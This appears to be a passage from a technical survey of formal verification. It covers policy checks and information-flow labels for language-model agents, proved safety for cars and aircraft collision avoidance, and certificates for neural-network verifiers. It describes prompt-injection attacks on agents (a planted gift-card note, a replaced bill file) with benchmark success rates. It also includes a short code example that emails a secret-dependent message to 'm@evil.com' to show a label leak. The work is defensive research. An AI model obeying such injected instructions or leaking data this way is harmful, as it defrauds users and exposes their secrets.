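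With ACL2's *partial-encapsulate*, the developer must ensure that all such results satisfy the stated constraints. ACL2 also blocks functional instantiation for these functions because it can't list every constraint a substitute would have to satisfy. A mistake can make a contradiction provable, as in Kaufmann and Moore's own toy example, which they simplified for explanation.

Using partial-encapsulate for a sampled language model would have the same effect as Kaufmann's attempt with the clock, because two different replies to the same message would both count as axioms. A network with fixed weights and exactly repeatable arithmetic would avoid this, and ACL2 could then prove what the network replies to a particular message. But each such theorem would cover a single input and depend on code outside ACL2, so it would be no stronger than a test.

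## Verified policy checks for language-model agents

The function `act` from the previous section is a small *policy check*, code that allows or denies each action an agent proposes before the agent carries it out. A real customer-service agent may have dozens of tools, and its rules refer to the company's database and to what happened earlier in the conversation. In 2026 several research groups wrote policy checks for such agents in Lean and proved theorems about the checks.

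### How LeanGuard decides on a call

In *LEANGUARD* (2026), Sankar, Ganguly and colleagues describe a shop's agent that is exchanging an item for a customer. One of its tools returns text in which an attacker has planted a note. The note claims that the customer has already approved the exchange and directs the agent to use the attacker's gift card. Planting instructions in this way is called *prompt injection*, and an agent without a policy check may simply obey. LeanGuard handles the resulting tool call in four steps:

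1. It intercepts the call before it reaches the tool and treats it as untrusted data.
2. An adapter looks up the relevant facts in the shop's database and in a journal of earlier events.
3. Compiled Lean code evaluates the policy's rules on the call, the facts and the journal.
4. If the rules allow the call, LeanGuard records it in the journal and then runs the tool. If not, the model can receive a list of the failed rules and a hint.

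Here LeanGuard denies the call because the gift card is not on the customer's account and the journal contains no confirmation. The note makes no difference, since text in a tool's output never counts as evidence. A confirmation is valid for one exact action and can be used once, so approval of one exchange can't authorize another.

Recording the call before running the tool prevents the common mistake of repeating an action that may already have succeeded. If a refund request times out, the refund may still have gone through, and a second attempt might pay the customer twice. Because the first attempt is already in the journal, a rule that allows only one refund blocks the second.

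A policy contains three types of rule. A *permit* makes an action eligible, and LeanGuard denies any action without one. A *requirement* must hold whenever it applies, and a *forbid* blocks an action outright. Rules can refer to the past with three operators:

- ONCE: a matching event happened earlier, such as the customer signing in.
- PREVIOUS: the last relevant event had some property, such as the agent's last look at this order showing it as pending.
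- SINCE: a condition has held without a break since some earlier event.

Each operator can have a time limit, for example to accept only confirmations from the last ten minutes.

Write c for the call together with the facts and the history. The decision is then:

```
allow(c)  ⇔  p(c) for at least one applicable permit p
             and r(c) for every applicable requirement r
             and not f(c) for every applicable forbid f
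             and no error occurred in evaluating the rules
```

The last line matters for rules that contain words like "not". Suppose a rule requires that the account not be flagged, and the account's record is missing. Code that treats a missing flag as false would conclude that the account is not flagged and allow the refund, but LeanGuard denies it. For the same reason, LeanGuard would deny the refund of "fifty" that the ACL2 rules approved earlier, if the policy read the amount as a number.

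### What the LeanGuard theorem covers

The code that evaluates the rules could contain mistakes, particularly in the operators that refer to past events. Sankar and colleagues therefore defined the meaning of a policy a second time, using LeanLTL, a Lean library for temporal logic. LeanLTL's operators look forward in time, so the definition lists the history from newest to oldest, and ONCE becomes "eventually" and SINCE becomes "until". Lean checks a proof that the code and the definition agree for every history.

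Theorem 1 states that, for every policy and every c, if LeanGuard returns "allow", then c satisfies the formula above under the LeanLTL definition. The runtime runs a tool only after that result. It follows that the agent cannot cause a change that the policy denies, provided that:

- the facts match the real state of the environment, and
- every call with consequences passes through the check.

Lean does not prove either condition. *Agenra* (2026) describes a similar check with a proved Lean core and gives the example of a compromised directory that returns a wrong address. The check then follows its rule correctly but approves a message to the wrong person. Rules about past events also require an accurate journal. *Formal Runtime Verification for Tool-Using LLM Agents* (2026) treats trustworthy records of where data came from as a prerequisite for enforcing such rules.

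The theorem also holds for every policy, including one that permits everything. To show that a particular policy is good, a developer has to prove a property of that policy. *Tether* (2026) proves that a policy preserves an invariant by induction on the sequence of actions, much like the ACL2 theorem run-stays-good. In one example, the invariant is that secret data never reach the agent's context. A language model writes the Lean proof or proposes a sequence of actions that breaks the invariant.

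### Results on customer-service tasks

Sankar and colleagues tested LeanGuard on τ²-bench, a benchmark in which an agent serves simulated customers under a written policy. They formalized the parts of the retail, airline and telecom policies that a check on tool calls can enforce, which took 45 rules for 43 tools and 583 lines of Lean. Five Qwen models, with 0.8 to 27 billion parameters, each attempted 278 tasks under three conditions:

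| | No check | LeanGuard, bare denial | LeanGuard with feedback |
|---|---|---|---|
| Forbidden calls executed | at least 33 | 0 | 0 |
| Episodes flagged by a model judge | 9.7% | 5.6% | 6.5% |
| Tasks completed | 72.7% | 68.9% | 70.9% |

The zeros follow from LeanGuard's design, because it runs only the calls it allows. The 33 forbidden calls occurred in 28 of 1,390 episodes, or 2%. In some of them, agents acted on a customer's phone line before identifying the customer. The true number of forbidden calls is probably higher, since replaying an old episode can't show whether a customer would have confirmed an action.

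The judge was a language model that compared each episode with the full written policy. It still flagged episodes under LeanGuard, although every executed call in them had satisfied the Lean rules. An audit sorted the 182 flagged calls from the two LeanGuard conditions by reason:

| Why the judge objected | Calls |
|---|---|
| It saw no consent for an action that LeanGuard had recorded as confirmed | 71 |
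| It could not see a fact in the records, such as that the customer was abroad | 37 |
| The Lean policy has no rule on the matter, such as when to transfer a customer to an employee | 69 |
| The call only read data | 5 |

In the second row, the judge was wrong. The third row mixes gaps in the formalization with complaints about things the written policy doesn't regulate either, such as the order in which the agent handles a customer's requests. In the first row, either side could be wrong. In the experiment, another language model stood in for the confirmation screen and sometimes recorded consent incorrectly. One recorded approval left out the customer's limit on the payment. LeanGuard then allowed a call that the customer had not really approved, and Theorem 1 remained true because the error was in the facts.

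"No forbidden calls" and "some flagged episodes" do not contradict each other, because the first result comes from checking the recorded facts against the formal rules, and the second comes from a fallible reader applying the written policy to what they could see.

The loss in task completion was statistically significant with bare denials but not with feedback, and nearly all of it came from the retail tasks. Agents that received feedback repeated blocked calls less often and recovered from 48 denials, compared with 34 for agents that received bare denials. Sankar and colleagues also had Lean search for a small change that would make a denied call acceptable. For 88 of the 252 denials that an edit could fix, Lean found a change and proved that the policy allows the edited call, typically in 2 milliseconds. Most of these changes sent a refund to the original payment method. The search ran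 only after the episodes ended, so nobody knows yet how much it would help a working agent.

### Results under attack

DTap is a benchmark of prompt-injection attacks, which are direct when the malicious instruction is in the prompt and indirect when it is in data that the agent reads. LeanGuard reduced the success rate of direct attacks from 57.9% to 5.9% and of indirect attacks from 22.3% to 3.8%, but the success rate on benign tasks also fell, from 53.1% to 12.5%.

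The policy in this experiment let the agent read the customer's records and public data but not change anything. In the travel, finance and legal tasks, no direct attack succeeded, and no benign task did either. About half of the lost benign tasks were medical ones in which LeanGuard had refused to register the patient. The telecom results were more encouraging because benign telecom tasks rarely need to change anything. The success rate of direct attacks fell from 55.1% to 2.4%, while benign success stayed at 75%. A deployment that permits ordinary bookings and payments would complete more tasks, but would presumably let some attacks through too. The experiment doesn't measure that trade-off.

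LeanGuard allowed no tool call that changed anything in any of the 289 attacks that still succeeded. The harm was in the agent's reply, such as a manipulated diagnosis or a request for card details under a pretext. A check on tool calls cannot stop such replies.

Sankar and colleagues list several other limitations. A language model drafted the formal rules and people corrected them, and the proofs can't reveal an error that both missed. All the agents came from one family of models, all the customers were simulated, and the judge was one of the models under test. The DTap policies covered seven of the benchmark's fourteen domains.

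### Tracking where data came from

An agent can also do harm with a call that looks permissible by itself. A payment to a new supplier may be fine if the account number came from the user but fraudulent if it came from a web page. *Information-flow control* attaches a label to every value, such as "untrusted" for text from the web or "secret" for an account balance. Anything computed from a labelled value inherits its label. A payment tool can then reject untrusted account numbers, and an email tool can reject secret contents.

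Labels are easy to get wrong, as this short program shows:

```
tmp  = True
rich = True
if balance > threshold: tmp = False
if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

If the balance is high, the third line changes tmp and labels it secret. The fourth line then does nothing, so rich keeps its value, True, and its public label. The email goes out because no value in it has a secret label. If the balance is low, no email goes out, so whether an email arrives reveals whether the balance is high. *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026) reports a leak of this type in CaMeL, a well-known defence against prompt injection.

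LLMbda is a small programming language for agents. A program can hold a conversation with a language model, copy or clear that conversation, and run code that the model writes. The conversation carries the labels of everything the program has sent, and each reply inherits them. If the reply is code, everything that code computes inherits them too. The interpreter stops a program that is about to change a public conversation based on a secret.

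The main theorem is a form of *noninterference*. Take two runs of a program whose inputs differ only in their secrets. Someone who sees only the public results should learn nothing about which run they are watching. Since a language model's replies are random, the theorem compares the probabilities of the results. It also has to allow for runs that produce no result because they never end or the interpreter stops them:

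| Public result | Probability with secret A | Probability with secret B |
|---|---|---|
| "yes" | 0.5 | 0.5 |
| "no" | 0.3 | 0.5 |
| none | 0.2 | 0 |

Garby and colleagues call two such distributions *compatible* if some third distribution, with a total of at most 1, gives every result at least as much probability as either of them. The two columns are compatible because the third distribution can give "yes" 0.5 and "no" 0.5. If A gave "yes" 0.6 and "no" 0.4, the columns would be incompatible, because the third distribution would need a total of 0.6 + 0.5 = 1.1. If both runs always produce a result, compatible distributions are identical. Otherwise, the distance between them is at most the average probability of no result, which is 0.1 here.

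The theorem is that the distributions are compatible for every program in the language, including those a language model writes during the run. The proof uses a modified version of the language's rules that skips a computation and returns a placeholder as soon as the computation's label becomes secret. The modified version never uses the secrets, so it gives the same distribution for A and B. It also produces each public result at least as often as the real version. Its distribution is therefore the third one the definition requires.

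The only information a run can still leak is whether it produced a result. That is at most one bit per run, but a loop that restarts the agent after each failure could leak a whole secret bit by bit. CaMeL has this problem because its retry loop is outside the part of the system that tracks labels. In LLMbda, the loop can be part of the program, and the theorem then covers it.

The same theorem guarantees that untrusted text cannot influence any result the interpreter labels as trusted, though it may cause a run to produce no result. Useful agents need exceptions, for instance to sort an untrusted email into one of five categories and use the category in a reply. LLMbda provides an explicit command, endorse, to relabel such a value as trusted. A second theorem shows that endorsing a value never weakens the protection of secrets.

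### A proved interpreter

A theorem about a language does not rule out mistakes in the interpreter that runs it. LLMbda's interpreter is a Lean function that takes the model's replies from an oracle, as in Kaufmann's model of system calls. Garby and colleagues proved that if the oracle draws replies at random with the model's probabilities, the interpreter produces each outcome with exactly the probability that the language's rules assign to it. The same function runs the agent, with real replies in place of the random oracle.

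The proof does not cover the code that sends the network request, and the theorem assumes that the probabilities of a reply depend only on the conversation. LLMbda also treats all data sources as part of the program. The experiment simulated the bank account and the files in the language itself, so an agent with real tools would need further code that the theorems do not cover.

The experiment used the banking tasks of AgentDojo, another benchmark for prompt injection. Attacks succeeded in two of 1,296 attacked runs. This result somewhat overstates how effective the labels were, because in 97 of the 144 combinations of task and attack, the attack needed a tool that the agent's plan would never contain. The other 47 combinations account for 423 runs, including both successes. In both successes, the user had told the agent to pay a bill according to a text file that the attacker had replaced,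 and the agent endorsed the file's contents and made the payment.

Without the `endorse` command, the interpreter blocks this attack, but it also blocks legitimate requests to pay the bill in a file. No label can establish whether the file contains the right bill. With Qwen3.7-plus, removing the command reduced completed tasks from 36 of 48 to 30. Even so, an agent with GPT-5.2 completed 36 of 48 tasks in LLMbda when nobody attacked it, compared with 18 for CaMeL with its policies switched on.

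### Checking the plan of work

Policy checks and labels restrict what an agent may do. *Lean4Agent* addresses whether the agent's workflow makes sense, and only some of its checks are proofs:

| Layer | Example of a fault | Basis of the check |
|---|---|---|
| 1. Structure | A step uses results that never leave the parallel branches that produced them | Lean, with no assumption about the language model |
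| 2. Conditions before and after each step | A step expects a summary that the previous step doesn't produce | Lean, assuming LLMExec |
| 3. Record of a run | The agent treats a bug as fixed although tests still fail | Lean or Python for precise conditions, a model judge for the rest |

LLMExec, from the previous section, assumes only that the language model *can* produce suitable output, so layer 2 shows at most that a successful run is possible. A language model also writes the conditions, and when a condition is stated only in English, Lean checks little beyond whether the variable exists.

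On difficult programming problems, agents solved 58% with workflows that passed layer 2 and 43% with workflows that failed it. This comparison used only three workflows of each kind, so part of the difference may be due to those particular workflows. A follow-up gives more evidence that the difference is related to what layer 2 checks. One failing workflow ran its steps without access to the earlier conversation. With that access restored, the workflow passed the check, and GPT-5.2's success rate rose from 52% to 62%.

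### Who writes the rules and supplies the facts

*VeriGuard* (Miculicich, Parmar and colleagues, 2025) automates more of the work. A language model turns a request such as "the agent cannot send emails outside the company" into a policy written in Python and a list of formal constraints. Nagini, a verifier for Python, then tries to prove that the code satisfies the constraints, and the model revises the code if the proof fails. When the agent runs, a language model reads the agent's text and extracts the values the policy needs.

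The proof therefore shows that code written by a model satisfies constraints also written by a model, and the code runs on facts that a model extracted. Miculicich and colleagues acknowledge that a person must confirm that the constraints match what the user meant. LeanGuard gets its facts more safely, because it takes them from the database where it can. On Mind2Web-SC, a benchmark of rules about who may do what on websites, VeriGuard with GPT-4o made the right decision in 95.1% of cases, so its proved policies were still wrong in about 5%.

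On another benchmark, VeriGuard and a language model that judged each action against the request both reduced successful attacks to zero, but agents completed more of their tasks with VeriGuard. When Miculicich and colleagues added VeriGuard's components one at a time, successful attacks fell to zero before they added the formal proof, so this measurement can't show what the proof contributed.

*AGENTSPEC* (Wang, Poskitt and Sun, 2025) presents a language for rules with a trigger, a condition and a response. For example, a rule can require the agent to ask the user before making a bank transfer to somewho is not a family member. AgentSpec does not prove that the rules work, but in tests they prevented over 90% of unsafe code executions. This result depends heavily on conditions such as "this command is destructive", which are checked by ordinary code that may overlook a dangerous command.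 A rule can also respond by having the language model examine its own plan, which offers no guarantee.

### How much of a policy a check can enforce

*Don't Make Models Guess Security and Safety* (Hong, She et al., 2026) examined 80 safety and security benchmarks for agents. Of these, 61% had no stated requirements for the agent's behaviour, and another 24% had only vague goals, such as refusing anything "unsafe", which leaves a developer with nothing to formalize.

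For three benchmarks, they classified each requirement by whether ordinary code could enforce it:

| Benchmark | Enforceable requirements |
|---|---|
| τ²-bench (airline bookings) | 42 of 51 |
| CAR-bench (voice assistant in a car) | 17 of 18 |
| MedAgentBench (medical records) | 34 of 57 |
| Total | 93 of 126 (74%) |

MedAgentBench came without a policy, so language models wrote one for the study. Its figure is therefore weaker evidence of what hospitals would require. The total also counts every requirement equally, regardless of how serious a violation would be.

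Of the 93 enforceable requirements, 88 need only simple checks, such as comparing the customer's name with the name on the ticket. The other five need rules about the order of events or the flow of information. A short comparison is easy to review by hand, so there is less reason to use a proved evaluator in many applications. LeanGuard uses operators over past events for some τ²-bench rules, but a developer can often store the relevant fact, such as "this customer has signed in", and check that instead. The proofs are more useful for agents whose rules depend on long histories, or that run code written by a language model.

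Hong and colleagues then added such checks to agents based on GPT-4o and GPT-5. Without them, the agents broke at least one enforceable requirement in 20% to 78% of tasks, depending on the model and the benchmark. The rate in the LeanGuard experiment was only 2%, partly because it excludes missing consent and counts only calls that changed something. With the checks, Hong's agents broke none of these requirements and completed more tasks on every benchmark. The gains ranged from slight to substantial, with completion on CAR-bench rising from 59% to 72%. Checks don't always raise completion, as LeanGuard's small losses show, but a check that explains its denials need not make an agent much less useful.

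The remaining quarter of the requirements concern tone, invented information, the order of steps in a conversation, and matters of judgement. One airline rule forbids the agent to offer compensation unless the customer explicitly asks for it. Hong and colleagues point out that a developer could enforce a cruder version, which blocks compensation until the customer's message is exactly the word "compensation". A prover could verify that version completely, but it would block compensation for a customer who wrote "I want my money back".

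## Learned controllers inside a proved safe region

A policy check can simply deny a tool call, but a moving car needs a safe manoeuvre to fall back on. A proof about the car also has to cover its motion between decisions.

### A car that must be able to stop

A car's software makes decisions at separate moments, while the car moves continuously. Engineers call this combination a *hybrid system* and describe the motion with differential equations, which give the rate at which each quantity changes. If d is the distance to an obstacle, v the speed and a the acceleration, the equations are d' = −v and v' = a, where the prime means "rate of change".

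*Differential dynamic logic*, which André Platzer developed, allows such equations inside programs and such programs inside formulas. Its theorem prover is KeYmaera X. The programs have these parts:

| Notation | Meaning |
|---|---|
| x := e | set x to e |
| x := * | set x to any value at all |
| ?Q | continue only if Q is true |
| {x' = e & Q} | let x change at rate e for any length of time, as long as Q stays true |
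| α ; β | run α, then β |
| α ∪ β | run either α or β |
| α* | repeat α any number of times |

The formula [α]P means that P is true after every possible run of α.

A car moving at speed v that brakes with a constant deceleration b stops in v/b seconds. Its average speed while braking is v/2, so it needs a free distance of v²/(2b) ahead. With b = 5 metres per second squared, that distance is 40 metres at 20 metres per second and 160 metres at twice that speed.

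The software also needs time to react. If it makes a decision at least every T seconds, then an acceleration of a may last for T seconds before the car can brake. In that time the car covers vT + aT²/2 and reaches a speed of v + aT. The acceleration is therefore safe if

room(a):  d ≥ vT + aT²/2 + (v + aT)²/(2b)

With T = 0.5, the distances at 20 metres per second are:

| Action until the next decision | Free distance required |
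|---|---|
| brake fully | 40 m |
| keep the same speed | 50 m |
| accelerate at 2 m/s² | 54.35 m |

If 52 metres are free, the car may keep its speed but may not accelerate at that rate. The whole claim, for positive b and T and a maximum acceleration A, is one formula:

```
v ≥ 0 and d ≥ v²/(2b)  →
[ ( ( a := −b  ∪  (a := *; ?(0 ≤ a ≤ A and room(a))) );
    t := 0;
    {d' = −v, v' = a, t' = 1  &  v ≥ 0 and t ≤ T}
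  )* ]  d ≥ 0
```

In each round the software either brakes fully or picks any acceleration that passes the test, and the car then moves for at most T seconds. The formula states that the car never passes the obstacle, however many rounds there are. (It leaves out gentle braking, which needs an extra case for a car that stops before the next decision.)

The invariant is d ≥ v²/(2b), which means the car can still stop in time. While the car brakes, d and v²/(2b) both shrink at the rate v, so the inequality stays true. This step uses only the rates of change, without solving the equations. If the car doesn't brake, room(a) already includes the distance it needs.

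KeYmaera X reduces such a claim to formulas about real numbers, which algorithms can in principle always decide, though sometimes far too slowly. *Overview of Logical Foundations of Cyber-Physical Systems* (Platzer, 2019) reports that the part of the prover that must be correct is under 2,000 lines long. KeYmaera X normally also relies on Mathematica or Z3 for the arithmetic.

### Letting a learned controller choose

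The expression a := * doesn't specify how the software picks an acceleration, so the theorem covers any method of picking one, just as the ACL2 theorem about the refund agent covered any function propose. This leads to a design with three parts:

1. A proved condition determines which actions are safe in the current state.
2. A learned controller proposes an action, for reasons such as comfort or fuel.
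3. If the action fails the condition, the software carries out a proved fallback, here full braking.

The fallback is always available because the invariant guarantees enough room for it. A person can also take the place of the learned controller. Kouskoulas, Platzer and Kazanzides (2013), in *Formal Methods for Robotic System Control Software*, model a surgical robot and a surgeon holding the same tool. Near a forbidden boundary, the robot scales down the tool's speed in proportion to the remaining distance. In a simplified one-dimensional model, the prover shows that the tool never crosses the boundary, whatever force the surgeon applies.

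Other traffic makes the condition more complicated. Prebet and colleagues assume that the car in front may brake at any moment with the greatest deceleration any car can reach, while the controlled car is guaranteed only a smaller one. If both cars drive at 30 m/s, and the front car can brake at 8 m/s² and the controlled car at 5 m/s², the front car needs 56.25 metres to stop and the controlled car needs 90. The gap must therefore exceed 33.75 metres. Half a second of reaction time at constant speed adds 15 metres.

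Platzer's overview also summarizes 2018 work by Nathan Fulton and Platzer on *reinforcement learning*, in which software tries actions and becomes more likely to repeat those that turn out well. The simplest approach is to train the controller freely and add the proved condition only when the car goes into use. The controller may then perform poorly, because its choices are overridden in a way they weren't during training.

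Fulton and Platzer therefore also applied the condition during training. The controller learns immediately that an action was dangerous, instead of tracing a crash back to a decision made much earlier, and training converged significantly faster. However, the controller may come to depend on being overruled, and it learns nothing about situations outside the safe region unless it can explore them in simulation.

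For those situations, Fulton and Platzer rewarded the controller for returning towards the safe region. It recovered in their experiments, but experiments don't prove that it always will. In 2019 they proved safety for a controller with several candidate models of the world. The controller takes only actions that are safe under every model it hasn't yet ruled out, so the proof assumes that at least one of the models, or a suitable modification of one, is right.

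### The ACAS X advisory table

ACAS X, a system for airliners developed under the US Federal Aviation Administration, tells pilots to climb or descend when another aircraft comes too close. Its advice comes mainly from a table of scores that an optimization program computed in advance, balancing the risk of collision against the disruption of unnecessary warnings. As with a trained network, no person wrote the table's decisions or could read through them all. Platzer estimates that writing the table as a program for the prover would take about half a trillion cases.

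Jeannin, Ghorbal and colleagues (2015), in *Formal Verification of ACAS X, an Industrial Airborne Collision Avoidance System*, left the table out of the proof. For each advisory, they worked out a *safe region*, the set of positions and speeds from which following the advisory prevents a near-collision, defined as two aircraft coming within 500 feet horizontally and 100 feet vertically of each other.

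Suppose two aircraft are in level flight at the same altitude, and the pilot of one is told to climb at 1,500 feet per minute, or 25 feet per second. The model assumes an upward acceleration of at least a quarter of gravity, about 8 feet per second squared. The aircraft reaches its climbing speed within about 3 seconds. From then on, its height gain after t seconds is at least 25t − 39 feet, which reaches 100 feet at about 5.6 seconds. If the aircraft will take at least that long to come within 500 feet of each other horizontally, the advisory is safe for a pilot who reacts immediately. For slower pilots, the model allows a delay during which the aircraft may accelerate in the wrong direction at up to a third of gravity.

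Jeannin and colleagues used the prover KeYmaera, a predecessor of KeYmaera X, to verify that no near-collision can occur if every advisory respects its safe region. They described each region in two ways and proved the descriptions equivalent. One refers to all future times, which suits the proof. The other is a list of inequalities about the present state, which a computer can check quickly against the table.

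They then checked all 648,591,384,375 points of the table. Assuming a three-second delay, they found 15,160,434,734 counterexamples (2.3%), where the table's advice violated the safe region although another advisory would have satisfied it. The remaining 97.7% includes points for which no advisory could be proved safe, so it is not the rate of safe advice.

In one counterexample, an aircraft is climbing at 3,000 feet per minute towards another that is 1,200 feet higher and descending at the same rate. They would pass each other's altitude while still well apart horizontally. If the first pilot follows the table's advice not to climb by levelling off, the aircraft nearly collide about 20 seconds later. The main cause was an inaccurate estimate of the horizontal timing, which the developers set out to improve.

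Many other counterexamples were less serious because the model assumed that the pilot follows the first advisory forever, whereas ACAS X can correct it a second later. Jeannin, Ghorbal and colleagues therefore proved a weaker condition in *A Formally Verified Hybrid System for Safe Advisories* (2016), which accepts an advisory if a later one can still prevent the near-collision. Checking the table against this condition for 16 combinations of delay and acceleration took about eight days on a cluster with 480 processor cores. The number of counterexamples ranged from 31.6 million to 898.7 million. In a further 11 to 14 billion states, no available advisory met the condition.

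The proof covers the safe regions, but Jeannin and colleagues call the comparison with the table a thorough test, "not a verification". They checked only the table's points, while in flight ACAS X interpolates between them. It also makes corrections, for example near the ground, which they left out. They assumed perfect sensors and an intruder that flies in a straight line. *Formally Verified Next-Generation Airborne Collision Avoidance Games in ACAS X* (Cleaveland, Mitsch and Platzer, 2021) treats the encounter as a game in which the intruder can manoeuvre too.

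### Proving that a network never needs the fallback

A neural controller could be safe without supervision if it never proposed an action that the condition rejects. Teuber, Mitsch and Platzer (2024), in *Provably Safe Neural Network Controllers via Differential Dynamic Logic*, prove this by checking a statement about a single decision:

for every state s that satisfies the invariant: allowed(s, network(s))

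For the braking car, the network would have to choose a permitted acceleration whenever d ≥ v²/(2b). This requirement includes no reference to time because the proof in differential dynamic logic already covers any number of permitted decisions.

Teuber and colleagues applied the method to neural networks for vertical collision avoidance, using safe regions that Jeannin's group had proved for ACAS X. They considered only intruders in level flight and analysed eight cases, which differed in the previous advisory. The networks were safe when that advisory was "do not climb" or "do not descend". In the other six cases, they found between 5,259 and 49,428 regions of counterexamples. In one counterexample, the network tells the pilot to climb and then reverses the advice, leading to a near-collision six seconds later. Even the two safe cases had counterexamples once the intruder could climb or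 descend. The two safety proofs also don't cover the decision to give no advice.

A controller can perform well in trials and still fail in this way. Teuber and colleagues also trained a controller to steer an airship through changing winds. It performed very well on average, but the analysis showed that it was unsafe in large parts of the state space because unlikely gusts could make it fail.

Prebet and colleagues used the same approach for highway driving and discovered that the simulator did not match its written specification. In the specification, "brake" always slows a moving car, but in the simulator's default setting it only lowers a target speed by one step, so a car travelling at 10 metres per second with a target of 20 would respond to "brake" by speeding up to 15. They changed this setting and trained a new network, but the analysis found that it was unsafe too. Examples from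 the analysis led to 538 crashes in the simulator's default environment. This count doesn't measure the risk on an ordinary trip, because the analysis searched for states in which the network fails.

### ModelPlex and the moment the model stops fitting

Every proof above assumes that the vehicle moves as the equations describe. ModelPlex, a method built into KeYmaera X, turns a proved model into tests that software can run while the vehicle operates. Each test is a formula relating the values before a step to the values after it, and ModelPlex produces a proof that the formula is correct. One test checks whether the controller's action was among those the model permits. For the braking car, the new acceleration must be −b or satisfy room(a). Another test checks whether the motion measured since the last decision is possible in the model.

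Suppose the car brakes for half a second from 20 metres per second. With b = 5, the model predicts that it covers 9.375 metres and slows to 17.5 metres per second. If the sensors measure 19 metres per second instead, the deceleration was only 2 m/s², perhaps because the road is icy. The test fails because the observed motion doesn't fit the model.

If the proposed action is unsafe, the software can veto it and brake instead, and the safety proof still applies. If the car's motion doesn't fit the model, the discrepancy has already happened. The software can still brake, warn the driver or hand over control, but the proof no longer guarantees that any of these will work. On this road, the car needs 100 metres to stop from 20 metres per second, and the condition may have reserved only 40. No test of past motion could have revealed the ice before the car reached it. To keep the guarantee on ice,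 the developer would have had to use the lower deceleration in the model from the start, which would also make the car keep much larger distances on dry roads.

The test also depends on sensor readings. *Verified Runtime Validation for Partially Observable Hybrid Systems* (Mitsch and Platzer, 2018) extends ModelPlex to systems whose state the software can only partly observe.

A model that is too exact causes the opposite problem, because harmless motion fails the test. Platzer's example is a model of a ball that bounces without losing energy. The model's safety proof is valid, but every real ball fails the resulting test. Prebet and colleagues had this problem with their highway simulator, which differed so much from the model that the full test would have switched off the safety condition in most states. They replaced the test with a check that the cars' state still satisfied the invariant.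 This check keeps the safety condition active but doesn't detect motion that contradicts the model's equations.

Ishii (2026), in *Verifying Autoware Controller Node by Combining Model Verification and Runtime Monitoring*, measured how often a full driving system fits a proved model. Autoware is open-source software for autonomous vehicles, and the part Ishii studied steers the car along a series of waypoints using conventional control methods, without a learned component. Ishii proved properties of a much simpler vehicle model in KeYmaera X, then wrote tests by hand in the style of ModelPlex and applied them to recordings of simulated drives in Tokyo's Shinjuku district. With tolerances of 0.2 metres and 0.8 metres per second, the stretches of driving fell into these groups:

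| | Simple simulator | Detailed simulator |
|---|---|---|
| Did not meet the model's starting conditions | 9.4% | 11.2% |
| Passed every test and reached the waypoint | 83.9% | 77.3% |
| Passed every test but missed the waypoint | 0% | 0% |
| Failed a test but reached the waypoint | 1.1% | 1.2% |
| Failed a test and missed the waypoint | 5.7% | 10.3% |

The model described roughly four fifths of the driving. With a tolerance of 0.05 metres, the share that passed every test and reached the waypoint fell to 63.9% and 43.7%. The zeros are encouraging but partly empirical, because the liveness theorem proves only that some sequence of control choices reaches the waypoint, not that Autoware follows such a sequence. Ishii ran the tests after the drives had ended and left using them to intervene during a drive for future work.

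## What can be proved about a neural network itself

A trained neural network is a fixed calculation made up of additions, multiplications and a few simple nonlinear steps, so it is possible to prove things about it as about other code. The usual theorem has this form:

for every input x in a region X: network(x) is in a set S

Teuber and colleagues proved a statement of this kind, that a controller chooses a permitted action in every state that satisfies the invariant. The most studied examples come from ACAS Xu, a version of ACAS X for unmanned aircraft. It uses 45 small networks, each of which scores five advisories and chooses the one with the lowest score. One property states that if the other aircraft is far away and much slower, the score for "clear of conflict" stays below a fixed limit.

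### Bounds and case splits

Each unit in such a network computes a weighted sum and applies a function called ReLU, which replaces negative numbers with 0. Desmartin, Isac and colleagues (2024), in *A Certified Proof Checker for Deep Neural Network Verification*, use a network with two of these units as an example:

```
h1 = ReLU(2·x1 + x2)
h2 = ReLU(x2 − x1)
y  = 2·h2 − h1
```

Suppose that both inputs lie between 0 and 1 and that y must stay below 1.5. The cheapest method computes a lowest and highest value for each quantity in turn:

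| Quantity | Lowest | Highest |
|---|---|---|
| 2·x1 + x2 | 0 | 3 |
| x2 − x1 | −1 | 1 |
| h1 | 0 | 3 |
| h2 | 0 | 1 |
| y | −3 | 2 |

The bound y ≤ 2 is true, but it is too loose to prove the requirement. It combines the highest value of h2 with the lowest value of h1, and no input produces both. h2 is 1 only when x1 is 0 and x2 is 1, and h1 is then also 1.

Splitting on the second unit gives the exact answer. The first unit needs no split because its sum is never negative.

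- If x2 ≥ x1, then h2 = x2 − x1, so y = x2 − 4·x1, which is at most 1.
- If x2 ≤ x1, then h2 = 0, so y = −2·x1 − x2, which is at most 0.

So y never exceeds 1, and it reaches 1 at the input (0, 1). ACL2 can prove this directly, since its fractions are enough for such a network:

```
(defun relu (z) (max z 0))

(defun net (x1 x2)
  (- (* 2 (relu (- x2 x1)))
     (relu (+ (* 2 x1) x2))))

(thm (implies (and (rationalp x1) (<= 0 x1) (<= x1 1)
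                   (rationalp x2) (<= 0 x2) (<= x2 1))
              (<= (net x1 x2) 1)))
```

This approach doesn't go far. Each ACAS Xu network has 300 units, which could require 2^300 cases, or about 10^90.

Specialized verifiers therefore try to avoid splitting. When z is between −1 and 1, ReLU(z) is never above the line (z + 1)/2. Putting that line in place of h2 gives

y ≤ (x2 − x1 + 1) − (2·x1 + x2) = 1 − 3·x1 ≤ 1

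Here a single line happens to give the exact maximum. In a larger network the errors of many lines add up, so the verifier splits the problem in two at one unit and tries again with tighter lines in each half. The leading verifier, α,β-CROWN, works this way and uses graphics processors to handle many cases at once.

### Certificates and verified checkers

Anyone can check a verifier's counterexample by running the network on that input. The claim that no counterexample exists is harder to check, and verifiers are large programs with bugs. *The 7th International Verification of Neural Networks Competition (VNN-COMP 2026)* (Ladner, Kaulen et al., 2026) reports that eight of the 13 competing tools returned at least one answer that was wrong or lacked a valid counterexample. The winner, α,β-CROWN, gave one such answer. An unfinished tool gave 955, partly because of a last-minute bug.

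Proving a whole verifier correct would be close to infeasible. The alternative is for the verifier to produce a *certificate*, a record of its reasoning that a much simpler program can check. The verifier Marabou produces a tree in which each branching splits a ReLU unit, and each leaf lists multipliers that expose a contradiction. For the network above, a certificate that y never reaches 1.5 needs one split and two leaves:

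```
Leaf 1, where y = x2 − 4·x1:
   1·(1 − x2) + 4·x1 + 1·(y − 1.5)  =  −0.5

Leaf 2, where y = −2·x1 − x2:
   2·x1 + 1·x2 + 1·(y − 1.5)  =  −1.5
```

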